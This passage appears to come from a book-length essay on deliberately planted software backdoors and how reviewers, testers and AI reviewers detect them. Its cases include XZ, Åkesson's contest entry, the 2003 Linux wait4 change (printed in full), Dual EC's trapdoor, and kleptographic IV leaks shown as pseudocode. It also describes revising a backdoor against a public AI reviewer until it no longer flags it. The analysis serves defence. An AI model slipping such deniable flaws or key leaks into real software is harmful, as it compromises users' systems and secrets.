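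In an interview for The Microsoft Threat Intelligence Podcast's *Behind the Scenes of the XZ vuln* (2024), Freund called it a myth that he noticed a login taking half a second too long. The story appears in popular accounts, including Mastronardi's *Half a Second* (2026). The delay was real, but he measured it later. A failed login took 0.299 seconds without the backdoor and 0.807 seconds with it, because the malicious code had to search through memory for the functions it needed. The backdoor turned itself off when somebody started sshd from a terminal in the usual way, and under some debugging tools. Freund then used the delay to tell whether the backdoor was active without attaching a debugger, by timing how long sshd took just to display its help text.

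He reported the backdoor privately on 28 March and publicly the next day. In April, Lins and colleagues wrote that they knew of no evidence that the attacker had used it. According to Mastronardi, nobody has identified the attacker.

Freund wrote that the discovery "really required a lot of coincidences", and Valsorda also thought it was chance. But Freund also said on the podcast Oxide and Friends that his roughly 15 years of work on PostgreSQL, much of it measuring performance, gave him a good starting point. Other people had also seen a symptom of the backdoor when the memory checker Valgrind reported errors in Red Hat's distributions on 4 March. Jia Tan gave a believable explanation and made a change that supposedly fixed the errors. The real fix came a day after that change, in new versions of the test files, which Jia Tan said were easier to reproduce.

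Tests that check whether a login accepts right passwords and rejects wrong ones give the same results whether it takes 0.3 seconds or 0.8, and specifications rarely limit the processor time spent on a rejected password. Measuring time and processor use is therefore useful against a deliberate attacker, who may prepare for the tests but not for everything somebody might measure. A distribution could record running time, memory errors and file sizes for every release and investigate sudden jumps. It would get false alarms, since honest changes also make programs slower or larger, and a more careful attacker could have made the backdoor's search faster. If Cox is right, a programming error also exposed Thompson's compiler. Attacks without such errors are less likely to become known, so these two cases probably make detection look easier than it is.

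### What would have stopped it

Building XZ directly from its repository would have stopped this attack. Freund found no active backdoor when he built it this way, and Arch switched to this method on 28 March. Some distributions can't easily do the same. NixOS used the hand-made package because the tools for building XZ from its repository themselves depend on XZ (Malka, 2025, *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor*).

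In the Debian discussion *Validating tarballs against git repositories* (2024), Vincent Bernat objected that the attacker would have adapted by putting the malicious script in the repository. Another participant replied that more developers build and test from the repository, which might have helped them notice it. That is probably true of busy projects, but XZ had very few people to notice anything. According to *Closing the Chain* (2025), Collin was taking a break from the internet when the backdoor was added.

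Lins and colleagues point out that reproducible builds alone don't protect against this kind of attack, because everyone who builds from the same backdoored package gets the same backdoored library. Debian's new reproducibility rule therefore doesn't protect against it either. The rule might still have caught the XZ backdoor by accident, since Freund found that the backdoor was sometimes missing when he rebuilt the library.

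Malka proposes building the library twice, once from the package and once from the repository, and comparing the results. When he tried this with the bad release on NixOS, the two libraries were identical, because the script activated only for Debian- and Red Hat-style packages. After he changed a setting to activate it, the library from the package was 258 kilobytes and the one from the repository was 210. Each distribution would therefore have to run the comparison under its own build conditions. Malka also has to assume that the suspect copy of XZ, which unpacks files during the build, doesn't tamper with the second library.

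Comparing the source files directly would be simpler, but the generated files cause too many harmless differences. *Verified Reproducible Tarballs* suggests making the packages reproducible, so that reviewers can spend their time on the repository. According to Malka, PostgreSQL already does this.

None of these comparisons would find a backdoor entirely in the repository. Limiting what the XZ library can do works wherever the attacker hides the code, and the simplest limit is not to load the library. On 29 February, a programmer proposed that systemd's library stop loading XZ automatically, and the project accepted the change on 5 March. Cox thinks the change would have defeated the attack, although distributions would first have had to adopt it.

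Lins and colleagues also discuss sandboxing, running a library as a separate process with few permissions. Android does this with the code that decodes media files. A sandboxed XZ library would receive compressed data and return decompressed data, with no access to sshd's table of functions. Lins and colleagues consider the loss of speed manageable but say sandboxing takes programmers a lot of work. In 2024 they knew of no general tool for it.

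A malicious library in a sandbox could still return altered data. Debian's package installer uses XZ to unpack software, so an altered file there could do as much damage as the login backdoor. However, altered output would violate XZ's specification, which requires decompression to reproduce the original data exactly. A proof of functional correctness would rule it out, even if the trigger needed a secret key, if the proof applied to the library people actually installed.

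## Malicious code disguised as a mistake, and how often reviewers find it

The XZ attacker hid compiled code in test files, where nobody could read it. An attacker can also leave malicious source code in full view and make it look correct. Wheeler calls this "maliciously misleading code" in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*. Double-compiling and reproducible builds can't expose it, so somebody has to find it by reading or testing the code.

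### A contest for innocent-looking code

Scott Craver, a professor of information security at Binghamton University, started the Underhanded C Contest in 2005. Entrants write short, readable C programs that secretly do something harmful. According to its *FAQ*, the contest was inspired by a 2004 contest for programs that count votes correctly in testing but miscount them on election day.

The 2015 round dealt with nuclear disarmament. Two countries have agreed to destroy warheads, and inspectors from each must confirm that the other is destroying real ones. A gamma-ray scan would show whether a warhead contains plutonium, but it would also reveal secrets about the weapon's design. The countries therefore put a program between the scanner and the inspector that compares the scan with a trusted reference and answers only yes or no. Entrants had to write the function at its centre:

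```
match(test, reference, bins, threshold)
```

Here `test` and `reference` are lists of counts, one for each energy level, `bins` is their length, and `threshold` sets how similar they must be. The function had to compare scans properly in general, but accept a fake warhead under rare conditions that the host country could create.

*Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (Craver, posting as XcottCraver, 2016) reports more than 40 entries. Entries earned more points for shorter, more readable code and for flaws that the author could pass off as honest mistakes if someone found them. Entrants explained their tricks in a separate file so that the judges could read the code before learning how it worked.

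About a third of the entries relied on NaN ("not a number"), which a computer produces when it divides zero by zero. Any comparison with NaN is false, so a program that rejects a warhead when `score < threshold` and accepts it otherwise will accept a warhead whose score is NaN. Few of these entries made the judges' shortlist, partly because experienced C programmers look closely at any division without a check for zero. One runner-up, Josh Lospinoso, left one letter out of `isinf`, which tests whether a number is infinite. The result, `sinf`, is also a real function, but it calculates a sine, which is almost never zero and so nearly always counts as true.

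### The winning entry

Linus Åkesson won with 66 lines of code, which he published with an explanation on his page *Faking Fissile Material* (2016). In outline, the program works like this:

```
match(test, reference, bins, threshold):
    if total(test) < threshold * total(reference):
        return NO
    t = preprocess(test)
    r = preprocess(reference)
    if spectral_contrast(t, r) >= threshold:
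        return YES
    return NO
```

The first check rejects objects that give off too little radiation. Preprocessing then removes noise and brings out the peaks. Finally, `spectral_contrast` treats the two lists as vectors and calculates the cosine of the angle between them, (*t* · *r*) / (|*t*| |*r*|), which is 1 when the peaks have the same positions and relative sizes. This is a standard way to compare spectra, and every step does what its name suggests.

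Åkesson divided the program into three files, and the flaw is a line missing from one of them. Another, `match.h`, defines the number type `float_t` as double precision, which takes up 8 bytes. The file containing `spectral_contrast` should include `match.h`, but it includes a standard mathematics file instead, which on most modern machines defines `float_t` as a 4-byte number. The main program therefore passes 8-byte numbers to a function that reads them as 4-byte numbers. The compiler processes each file separately, so it doesn't detect the conflict. GCC can warn about this kind of omission, but only if the programmer turns the warning on.

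If each list has 1,000 numbers of 8 bytes each, the function reads 1,000 numbers of 4 bytes each, which covers only the first half of the list. The right half of the spectrum therefore has no effect on the comparison.

The function also misreads the half it covers, because it treats each 8-byte number as two separate numbers. One is always zero, since the counts are whole numbers small enough to leave the last 4 bytes empty. The other is a compressed version of the original. An 8-byte number uses 11 bits for its exponent, which sets its scale, while a 4-byte number uses only 8 bits. Dropping the last three bits of the exponent divides it by eight, which is roughly like taking the eighth root of the number. A value of 10 becomes 2.56 and a value of 1,000 becomes 4.48, so a hundredfold difference shrinks to less than twofold. The comparison still depends on where the peaks are, but hardly on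 how high they are.

A country could therefore present a warhead with a fraction of the expected plutonium, plus some other radioactive material with peaks in the right half of the spectrum. The extra material provides enough radiation to pass the first check, and `spectral_contrast` then ignores it. Åkesson also chose the preprocessing steps to suit the trick. For example, averaging over 16 values instead of 15 keeps those last 4 bytes empty, because dividing by a power of two adds no stray digits. Programmers routinely choose powers of two, however, and the documentation gives a plausible reason for each step.

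XcottCraver remarked that a reader who misses the confusion over `float_t` will find nothing else even slightly suspicious in the code. If someone does notice it, Åkesson can say he forgot to include a file, a mistake every C programmer makes.

### What an inspector would see from outside

An inspector who saw only the interface would have had the function's inputs, its yes-or-no answer and the documentation, which included Åkesson's test results. He generated 1,000 artificial materials, made two slightly different scans of each, and compared them with scans of different materials. The results separated well enough for him to recommend a threshold of 0.6. An inspector who repeated these tests would have found that the detector worked.

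The handmade forgery in Åkesson's explanation passes at any threshold up to 0.72, so it passes easily at the recommended setting. He also generated 1,000 crude forgeries, each made of 10% the right material and 90% something else, and a large proportion failed. These failures give the inspector little protection, because the host country can test forgeries with the program beforehand and present the one that scores best.

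However, this backdoor is much easier to find by testing than the password "vT9#kq2L". It affects the comparison of almost every pair of scans, and a tester can reveal it without knowing a secret. An inspector could take a genuine scan, move the peaks in the right half, and see that the answer stays the same. A more general method is to write a second program from the same documentation and compare the scores. The two programs would disagree on nearly every pair, much as a compiler carrying Thompson's attack fails to match a copy built another way. The function returns only yes or no, but an inspector who can set the threshold can find the score by raising the threshold until the answer changes. Running the program on an older 32-bit PC would also have revealed a problem, because `float_t` has a different size there and the program breaks.

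These tests seem obvious to somebody who knows the trick. An inspector who doesn't know it would have to suspect the author and spend days checking a program that had passed its tests. The sponsor's announcement, NTI's *“Underhanded C” Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies*, noted that there were no standards for writing or reviewing such software, so nothing would have required such a check.

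### One equals sign in the Linux kernel

In 2003, somebody tried a similar trick on Linux. The developers kept the kernel's source code in a system called BitKeeper and provided a copy in another system, CVS, for people who preferred it. On 5 November, Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, noticed a change in the CVS copy that had no link to a record of approval. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) explains that the change didn't exist in BitKeeper at all, and that someone had apparently broken into the CVS server to insert it. It added two lines to `wait4`, a function that lets one program wait for another:

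```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
    retval = -EINVAL;
```

In C, `==` compares two values, while `=` stores a value. With `==`, the second half of the condition would check whether the user is number 0, the system's administrator. The code has `=` instead, which makes the user the administrator, so any program that called `wait4` with that unusual pair of options would have gained full control of the machine.

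The missing record had exposed the change, and McVoy had already flagged it as improper, but he missed what it did. When another developer pointed out on the kernel mailing list that the change looked like a backdoor, McVoy (2003) replied in *Re: BK2CVS problem*, "Good eyes, I missed that." So an expert who already suspected two particular lines read them without noticing the missing character.

The `=` in `wait4` could have been a typing mistake, since writing `=` for `==` is one of the most common slips in C. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) argues that it was clearly intentional, because `wait4` doesn't need to deal with the user ID. Szepe (2003) pointed to the extra parentheses around `current->uid = 0`, which prevent a compiler warning. The parentheses are weak evidence, since the comparison before them has parentheses too and an honest programmer might have written both that way. InfoQ's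 argument is better, but kernel functions often check whether the user is the administrator. The break-in is much stronger evidence of intent than anything in the code. If a regular contributor had submitted the same two lines through the normal process, it would have been hard to disprove a claim that the `=` was a typing mistake.

### The University of Minnesota patches

In August 2020, Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu of the University of Minnesota tested the normal review process by sending Linux developers a handful of patches, or proposed changes, under invented names. The patches appeared to fix small bugs but were meant to introduce more serious ones. Wu and Lu called them "hypocrite commits" and presented the experiment in a paper as evidence that an attacker could get vulnerabilities into open-source software this way. They said they had stepped in before any faulty patch was added to the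 kernel.

The dispute became public in April 2021, when another member of the group sent patches that the kernel developers found useless or wrong. Greg Kroah-Hartman, one of the most senior developers, accused the group of experimenting on them again and banned contributions from the whole university. The sender said the patches came from a new automatic bug-finding tool. Critics of the original study objected that it had used volunteers as test subjects without their consent and wasted their time. The university's ethics board had decided that the study didn't count as research on human subjects. The researchers apologised and withdrew the paper.

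In May 2021, the Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board reported that the kernel's reviewers had rejected or ignored every invalid patch from the experiment. That is encouraging, but a handful of patches is too few to estimate a detection rate, and a reviewer may ignore a patch without noticing what is wrong with it.

The board's wider audit may be more informative. Developers re-reviewed 435 changes from people at the university, most of them from years of ordinary work. The great majority were correct, but 39, about 9%, still needed fixing. All 39 had passed review the first time, and there was no sign that anybody had planted the errors. If reviewers let honest mistakes through at anything like that rate, an attacker who imitates such mistakes has a fair chance of success.

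The audit also shows why it matters whether a flaw is deliberate, even though reviewers can't tell from the code. Both kinds of flaw need the same repair, but a deliberate one also casts doubt on everything else its author has contributed. In this case, suspicion about a few patches led dozens of developers to recheck hundreds. With code from an AI model, the same suspicion could extend to millions of lines.

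### How often human reviewers find flaws

The best-known study of how well people find security flaws in code used flaws that nobody had tried to disguise. In *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Security Code Review* (2013), Anne Edmundson and colleagues hired 30 developers to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. None found all seven. More experienced developers weren't reliably better, and developers who reported more real flaws also tended to report more false ones. Reviewers would presumably do worse against someone like Åkesson, who chose his flaw because people overlook it, but the contest didn't measure how many readers missed the flaw.

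### How often AI reviewers find planted backdoors

Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026), in *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, gave AI models a harder version of the task, with only compiled programs to examine. The software company Quesma built the test, BinaryAudit, with a reverse-engineering specialist. They added backdoors to open-source network software and removed the names that make machine code easier to follow. The models could use standard analysis tools and had to locate the malicious function, so a lucky guess wouldn't count. The backdoors were fairly obvious, and a skilled person could find them without much trouble.

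AI models quickly got better at finding backdoors in machine code in the year to February 2026. According to Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, Gemini 2.5 Pro (March 2025) found 21% of them, Gemini 3 Pro (November 2025) found 44%, and Claude Opus 4.6 (February 2026) found 49%. The newest models in the ranking date from early 2026, and today's models can probably do better.

One of the failures resembles McVoy's. The testers had added seven lines to dnsmasq, a program that assigns network addresses. Those lines run any command hidden in a certain kind of network message. Claude Opus 4.6 found the right function and the instruction that runs the command. Without checking where the command came from, it concluded that this was probably dnsmasq's normal way of running scripts and moved on.

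The models raised false alarms on 28% of clean programs on average. Suppose that one program in 1,000 contains a backdoor and a reviewer checks 100,000 programs. If it performs like Gemini 3.1 Pro, with 49% detection and 17% false alarms, it will find 49 of the 100 backdoors and raise about 17,000 false alarms, so only about one alarm in 350 will be real. Grabowski and colleagues want a false alarm rate below 0.001%, which would mean about one false alarm in this example. One version of GPT-5.2 had no false alarms and still found 46% of the backdoors, but the test had only 33 tasks in total, too few to show that a false alarm rate is anywhere near 0.001%.

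Reviewers have an easier job when they can compare the source code with its previous version. In *SEVRA-BENCH* (2026), Melo, Fogliato and colleagues gave eight AI reviewers about 1,000 changes that reintroduced flaws developers had already fixed, and the strongest reviewers rejected most of them. A reviewer that rejected every change would do even better on such a test, so the result is hard to interpret without a count of false alarms.

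The best figures that include both counts come from Lily, a conventional testing tool described in *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026). Lily runs the old and new versions of a program on large numbers of automatically generated inputs and records which services each version requests from the operating system, such as opening a file or starting another program. It raises an alarm if an input makes the new version request a combination of services that is unusual for that version and that the old version doesn't request on the same input.

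The test of Lily covered 13 backdoors, three of them from real attacks, and each run lasted ten minutes. One was a real backdoor from 2011 in vsFTPd, a file-transfer program, which gave full control of the machine to anyone whose username contained ":)". Lily found an input that triggered it and cut the code a person had to read from 1,407 changed lines to seven.

| Test | Planted backdoors found | False alarms on clean code |
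|---|---|---|
| Compiled programs, Gemini 3.1 Pro (Quesma) | 49% | 17% |
| Compiled programs, GPT-5.2 Codex at its highest setting (Quesma) | 46% | 0% |
| Single source changes, Lily (Kokkonis and colleagues) | 90% | 0.2% |
| Whole releases, Lily (Kokkonis and colleagues) | 83% | 4.3% |

The rows aren't directly comparable, because Lily always has an older version of the program to treat as clean, and somebody who receives an entirely new program from an AI model does not. Lily also has to find the trigger, so it would probably miss a backdoor that requires the attacker's signature, like the one in XZ. And it can detect only backdoors that request something unusual from the operating system. Åkesson's function requests nothing from the operating system and just does some arithmetic and returns the wrong answer, so Lily would have nothing to detect.

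### The PHP flaws of October 2026

AI reviewers' most striking successes have been with accidental flaws. In October 2026, the developers of PHP, a programming language used by about 70% of websites, released urgent fixes for two critical flaws. *PHP2Shell* (Constantin, 2026) reported OpenAI's statement that AI had found them before attackers did. According to *OpenAI says ChatGPT Sol helped uncover critical PHP flaws*, from Tom's Hardware, researchers working with AI turned a two-year-old bug that had stumped human developers into working attacks within two weeks. *AI uncovers massive flaw in web's foundational code* (Sabin, 2026) counts the discovery among the most consequential AI has made in security so far.

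There is no sign that anyone planted these flaws. They also can't be used to calculate a detection rate, because nobody knows how many other flaws the same audits missed. In 2021, however, attackers broke into PHP's code server and planted a backdoor, which developers removed before it reached a release. That backdoor is among Lily's 13, and Lily caught it in 16 of 20 runs.

Skill at finding accidental flaws should carry over to deniable backdoors, since the two can be identical. An AI reviewer that can find an exploitable mistake in PHP can find the same flaw when someone has put it there on purpose. Success with accidental flaws is less relevant to flaws that an attacker has tested against the same reviewer. Any attacker can run a public model on a draft and keep revising the draft until the model no longer flags it. Wheeler suggested that people who build tools to search for misleading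 code might keep them private, and Grabowski and colleagues expect defenders to need private models for the same reason.

### Why no checker can catch everything

Could a sufficiently good program detect all malicious code? Two mathematical results rule this out. In *Computer Viruses: Theory and Experiments* (1984), the computer scientist Fred Cohen defined a virus as a program that can alter other programs to include a copy of itself, possibly a changed one. Suppose somebody offers a perfect detector, `is_virus`, that always gives the right answer. Cohen considered a program along these lines:

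```
contrary():
    if is_virus(contrary):
        stop
    else:
        infect another program
```

If the detector classifies `contrary` as a virus, `contrary` stops without infecting anything, so it isn't a virus. If the detector classifies it as harmless, it infects another program, so it is a virus. The detector is wrong either way, so no perfect detector exists. `contrary` can refer to its own text with the trick Thompson used to make a program print itself.

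Henry Gordon Rice had proved something much more general in 1953. Rice's theorem concerns what a program does, as opposed to how its text looks. For any such property that some programs have and others lack, no checker can give the right answer for every program. The proof uses an earlier result of Alan Turing's, that no program can always determine whether another program will eventually stop. Take the property "never emails a password", and suppose that a perfect checker for it exists. For any program *P* and input *x*, build this one:

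```
Q():
    simulate P on input x, without letting it send anything
    email a password
```

`Q` reaches its second line only if *P* stops. The checker's answer about `Q` would therefore reveal whether *P* stops on *x*. Since Turing proved that no program can determine this in every case, the checker can't exist.

These theorems rule out a checker that is right about every possible program, but a reviewer has to judge only the programs in front of them, so searching for malicious code is not hopeless. Neither theorem implies that Åkesson's 66 lines are hard to check. The theorems also assume unlimited memory. A real computer has a finite number of states, so a checker could in principle examine them all, but there are far too many for this to help.

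A better reply is that a reviewer can accept only the programs they can establish are safe, and reject everything else. Such a reviewer will reject some harmless programs but need never accept a harmful one, and neither theorem rules that out. Linux already does this with eBPF programs, which are small programs that users can load into the kernel. Before one is loaded, a verifier tries to show that it will finish and will touch only the memory it is allowed to use. If the verifier can't, the kernel refuses the program, and programmers regularly have to rewrite harmless code to satisfy it. Rewriting takes an AI author little effort, so demanding simpler code is a more realistic remedy now than when people wrote everything.

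The reply works only if reviewers can tell when they don't understand something. A reviewer who rejected all confusing code would still have accepted Åkesson's program, because it isn't confusing. McVoy and Claude Opus 4.6 also thought they understood the lines they read. A reviewer who insists on a proof is in a stronger position. To prove that `match` calculates the cosine described in its documentation, the reviewer would have to show that `spectral_contrast` reads the same numbers that `match` passes to it. The proof would fail at that step because `spectral_contrast` reads different numbers, however innocent the code looked.

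## The Dual EC random number generator and backdoors no test can detect

Proving that a program meets its specification doesn't help if the backdoor is in the specification. That very probably happened with Dual EC, a method of generating random numbers that became a US government standard in 2006. Programmers who exactly followed the standard built the backdoor into their products without knowing it.

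### What a random number generator must do

When a browser connects to a bank's website, the two computers use random numbers to make secret keys. They also send some random numbers openly, so that nobody can replay an old conversation. Computers can collect only a little physical randomness, from events such as tiny variations in timing, so they use a pseudorandom number generator to stretch it into as many numbers as they need.

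The generator keeps a secret number called its state. For each request, it calculates a new state from the old one and an output from the new state. Anyone who learns the state can predict all later outputs. According to *Dual EC* (Bernstein, Lange and Niederhagen, 2015), the most important requirement is that nobody should be able to predict outputs from other outputs. An attacker who sees outputs sent openly must therefore be unable to work out the state from them.

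Tests can check that ones and zeros are equally common or that patterns don't repeat, but not whether somebody has a secret shortcut for computing the generator's internal state from its output.

### How Dual EC works

A toy version with small numbers shows the trick. It has two public numbers, P = 10 and Q = 5, and keeps only the remainder after dividing by 23:

```
new state = remainder of P^(old state)
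output    = remainder of Q^(new state)
```

Suppose the state is 7. The new state is 10^7 mod 23, which is 14, and the output is 5^14 mod 23, which is 13. On the next request, the state becomes 12 and the output is 18.

Someone who sees the 13 has to find out which power of 5 produced it. They can try every power when the numbers are this small, but nobody knows a practical way to do it with numbers hundreds of digits long. The designer of this generator, however, knows that P is the cube of Q, because 5^3 is 125, which leaves a remainder of 10. The designer can therefore get the next state by cubing the output, since 13^3 is 2,197, which leaves a remainder of 12. This works because (5^14)^3 equals (5^3)^14, which has the same remainder as 10^14.

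Dual EC does the same with points on an elliptic curve. These points are pairs of numbers (*x*, *y*) that satisfy an equation of the form *y*² = *x*³ + *ax* + *b*, again keeping only remainders. There is a rule for adding two points to get a third, and *s*P means P added to itself *s* times. A computer can calculate *s*P quickly even if *s* has 256 bits, but nobody knows a practical way to recover *s* from P and *s*P.

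The standard gives two public points, P and Q. Writing x(…) for a point's first coordinate, the generator starts from a secret state *s* and does this:

1. It calculates the new state, *s′* = x(*s*P).
2. It calculates x(*s′*Q), drops the first 16 of the 256 bits and outputs the other 240.
3. On the next request, it moves to the state x(*s′*P).

Now suppose that an attacker knows a number *d* for which P = *d*Q. One full output is enough to find the following state:

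1. The attacker tries all 2^16, or 65,536, possible values of the missing bits.
2. For each value, the attacker uses the curve's equation to find a point R with that first coordinate. About half the values have no such point and drop out.
3. The attacker calculates x(*d*R). For the right value, R is *s′*Q (or its mirror image, which gives the same result). Then *d*R = *ds′*Q = *s′*(*d*Q) = *s′*P, and x(*s′*P) is the following state.
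4. The attacker uses each candidate state to predict the next output and keeps the one that matches.

Everyone else would have to work out *d* from P and Q, which is the problem nobody knows how to solve.

However, the output wasn't perfectly random, because some 240-bit outputs have slightly more matching points on the curve than others and so come up slightly more often. Kristian Gjøsteen reported a bias to the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) in March 2006, and Berry Schoenmakers and Andrey Sidorenko published a stronger attack in May. Their work showed that Dual EC was a poor generator but didn't reveal the backdoor. If NIST had responded by making the generator drop many more bits, it would also have closed the backdoor, because the attacker would have had too many missing bits to guess.

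### A backdoor in the standard

NIST kept the bias and published the standard in June 2006. The design had come from the National Security Agency (NSA), the US intelligence agency that makes and breaks codes, though its role did not appear in any of the public documents.

In October 2004, John Kelsey of NIST asked Don Johnson, who had presented Dual EC at a workshop, where Q, one of the generator's two points, came from. Johnson replied that it was in essence the public key for some random private key. That private key is the secret an attacker would need. Johnson added that Q could have been generated so that nobody had such a key, but that the NSA had rejected the idea and he wasn't allowed to discuss it publicly. Ten years later, Kelsey wrote that he hadn't understood at the time why this mattered.

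Two Certicom employees had worked out the attack by January 2005, when they applied for a patent on both using and avoiding it. The application became public in July 2006, but hardly anyone noticed. In August 2007, Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson of Microsoft gave a short conference talk showing that whoever chose P and Q could have a backdoor. In response to the resulting criticism, NIST said it had no evidence that anyone had the secret number, and it left Dual EC in the standard.

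In September 2013, The New York Times reported that NSA memos leaked by Edward Snowden appeared to confirm that the agency had engineered the weakness. NIST advised people to stop using Dual EC that month. In December, Reuters reported that the NSA had paid RSA Security $10 million in a deal that made Dual EC the default in RSA's BSAFE software. NIST left Dual EC out of the revised standard it published in 2015.

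Nobody outside the NSA has shown that it has *d*. Richard George, a former technical director there, said in 2014 that the agency had wanted Dual EC for its own use and was happy for others to choose different points. But NIST's standard recommended against doing so, and a product with different points couldn't get government certification. George also said that nobody had shown the attack working in real life. By then, Bernstein, his colleagues and other researchers had nearly done so. They replaced the points in several products with a pair whose *d* they knew, then attacked the encrypted connections that browsers use. The attack took a small cluster of computers under three seconds for one version of BSAFE, about an hour for another, and up to about three hours for Microsoft's software.

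The fourth product examined, a version of OpenSSL, had passed government validation despite a bug that made Dual EC fail its self-test every time. Probably nobody had ever used Dual EC in this product.

By changing one constant, an intruder could presumably decrypt traffic from Juniper's firewalls. Juniper used Dual EC with its own Q. As Matthew Green explained in his post on the Juniper backdoor, somebody broke into the company's code and replaced that Q with another. Juniper had meant to pass the output through a second generator before anyone saw it, which would have blocked the attack, but a bug skipped that step. To a reviewer, the change would look like one long, meaningless number replacing another, and the generator would pass the same tests as before.

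One could prove that a program implements Dual EC correctly, and could prove the same of Juniper's altered version if the specification contained the altered Q. The specification leaves out the requirement that nobody knows *d*. No test or proof about the program can establish this, because it isn't a fact about the program. A reviewer can only ask how somebody chose the constants, as Kelsey did, and reject them unless others can check the answer. For example, a designer can put a published phrase through a hash function, which turns any input into a fixed-length, random-looking number, and use the result as the first coordinate of Q. Anyone can repeat the calculation, and the designer has no practical way to find the matching *d*.

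### The unexplained seeds behind US elliptic curves

Unexplained constants can also be harmless. In 2000, NIST published a set of elliptic curves that much of the internet came to rely on. For each curve, the standard gives a seed, an arbitrary number that goes through a hash function to produce part of the curve's equation. The NSA supplied the seeds, and Anthropic's *Claude reveals ECDSA curve origins* (2026) recounts that the agency did not explain where they came from. Dual EC runs on the same curves, but *Bounty to Recover NIST’s Elliptic Curve Seeds* (2023) points out that its constants are separate from these seeds.

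Hashing a seed to generate a curve stops a designer from choosing the curve directly, but the designer can still try many seeds. If the NSA knew of a secret weakness that affected one curve in a million, it would need to try about a million seeds to find one that produced a weak curve. *How to manipulate curve standards* (Bernstein, Chou and colleagues, 2014) found that the difficulty of such an attack depends on what justification the public will accept for a curve. If the public accepts an unexplained seed, the designer can try as many seeds as their computing power allows.

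The usual story about the curve seeds was that Jerry Solinas of the NSA had made them by hashing a joke like "Give Bob and Jerry a raise" and then forgotten the wording. People spent years trying to guess the sentence. In October 2026, researchers at Anthropic used Claude to find that someone had instead started `drand48`, an ordinary random number generator, from the computer's clock and tried its output as seeds until one gave a valid curve.

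Filippo Valsorda, who had offered a reward for the answer, wrote his own program to check it. *The NIST Elliptic Curves Seeds Bounty Has Been Claimed* (Valsorda, 2026) reports that the seed for P-256, one of these curves, is the 1,842nd that the generator produces when started from 01:52:34 GMT on 16 August 1997.

This nearly rules out a backdoor, because it leaves so few seeds to choose from. Even if the NSA could have picked any of the roughly 63 million seconds in 1997 and 1998, and any of the first 16 suitable curves, it had only about a billion (2^30) options. The attack some cryptographers had worried about relied on choosing among 2^70 seeds, about a trillion times as many.

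The method produces roughly twice as many valid seeds as NIST published, and nobody knows why the NSA skipped the others. Valsorda suggests a bug may be the cause, and the figure of 16 curves takes the skipping into account. A billion options would still be enough to find a curve with a weakness that affects one in a million. But public researchers would have had to miss such a weakness for more than 25 years, and choosing seeds by the clock would be an odd way to exploit it.

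Nobody could have told from the seeds alone that they were chosen honestly. Finding an explanation took 26 years, though the standard could have included it in a short note from the start.

### Leaking a key through valid outputs

An attacker doesn't need to change the specification if it lets the program choose its own random numbers. Adam Young and Moti Yung began studying such attacks in the 1990s and named the field kleptography. In *Security of Symmetric Encryption against Mass Surveillance*, Bellare, Paterson and Rogaway (2014) worked out when these attacks are possible for programs that encrypt and decrypt with the same secret key. They use the term "algorithm-substitution attack" for replacing an honest encryption program with one that leaks.

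Many encryption programs mix a fresh random value, the initialisation vector or IV, into each message, so that sending the same message twice gives different results. The IV travels openly with the encrypted message because the receiver needs it. A malicious program could do this:

```
encrypt(key, message):
    iv = scramble(attacker_key, key)
    return iv, honest_encrypt(key, iv, message)
```

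A version without the backdoor would set `iv` to a random number. Here, `iv` is the output of `scramble`, a standard cipher that encrypts the user's key with the attacker's key. The receiver can decrypt the message as usual, because any IV is allowed. An attacker watching the network can decrypt the IV to get the user's key, then read everything encrypted with it.

This simple version would use the same IV every time, which somebody might notice. Bellare and colleagues avoid this by scrambling one randomly chosen bit of the key at a time, along with its position and some random filler. With a 128-bit key, the attacker needs about 620 messages to collect every bit.

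A tester can't detect the backdoor if the scrambling cipher is good, meaning that its output looks random to anyone without the attacker's key. Any test that could distinguish these IVs from random ones would also break the cipher. This holds even for a tester who knows the user's own key.

A program can leak the user's key even when the IV is hidden. It encrypts a message, applies a secret yes-or-no test to the result, and tries again with new randomness until the answer matches the next bit of the key. Each message takes two tries on average and leaks one bit, so 128 messages leak a 128-bit key. The attack provably works on practically any encryption scheme that uses random values and keeps no record between messages, even if the scheme has only seven bits of randomness per message.

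Someone who reads the code could still spot the attack, and could also use it, because the code contains `attacker_key`. Young and Yung's versions prevent the reader from using it by putting only a public key in the program, as the XZ attacker did. A proof that the IV comes straight from the system's random number generator could also help, but the generator would then need checking too, in case it is something like Dual EC.

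Bellare and colleagues also proved that some encryption schemes can't leak in this way. In these schemes, the receiver's program accepts exactly one encrypted form of the message for any given key, message and position in the conversation. A malicious program whose output must decrypt correctly therefore has to send exactly what the honest program would have sent, so the attacker learns nothing extra. One way to build such a scheme is to have both sides count messages and use the count in place of a random IV. Removing randomness from the honest program isn't enough by itself. If the receiver accepts two different amounts of padding, for instance, a malicious program can leak one bit by choosing between them.

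This result assumes that everything the malicious program sends decrypts correctly. Users would notice frequent failures, but they might miss one that almost never happens. For example, a program could output the key when asked to encrypt one particular 128-bit phrase and behave honestly otherwise. In *A More Cautious Approach to Security Against Mass Surveillance*, Degabriele, Farshim and Poettering (2015) argue that this innocent-looking assumption in the 2014 analysis severely limits the attacker. The proof also does not cover leaks through timing or other parts of a system, such as the random numbers that two computers exchange before they start encrypting.

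### Undetectable backdoors in trained models

Reading ordinary code is at least a possible defence against backdoors. A machine learning model is harder to read because its behaviour depends on many numbers, called weights, that are set during training. Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) proved in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* that some backdoors in models are undetectable even to someone who can examine every weight.

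Their example is a bank that pays an outside company to train a model that approves or rejects loans. The bank tests the model on past applications and finds it accurate. But the company has kept a secret key that lets it reverse any decision by altering the application very slightly, perhaps in the last digits of the amount requested.

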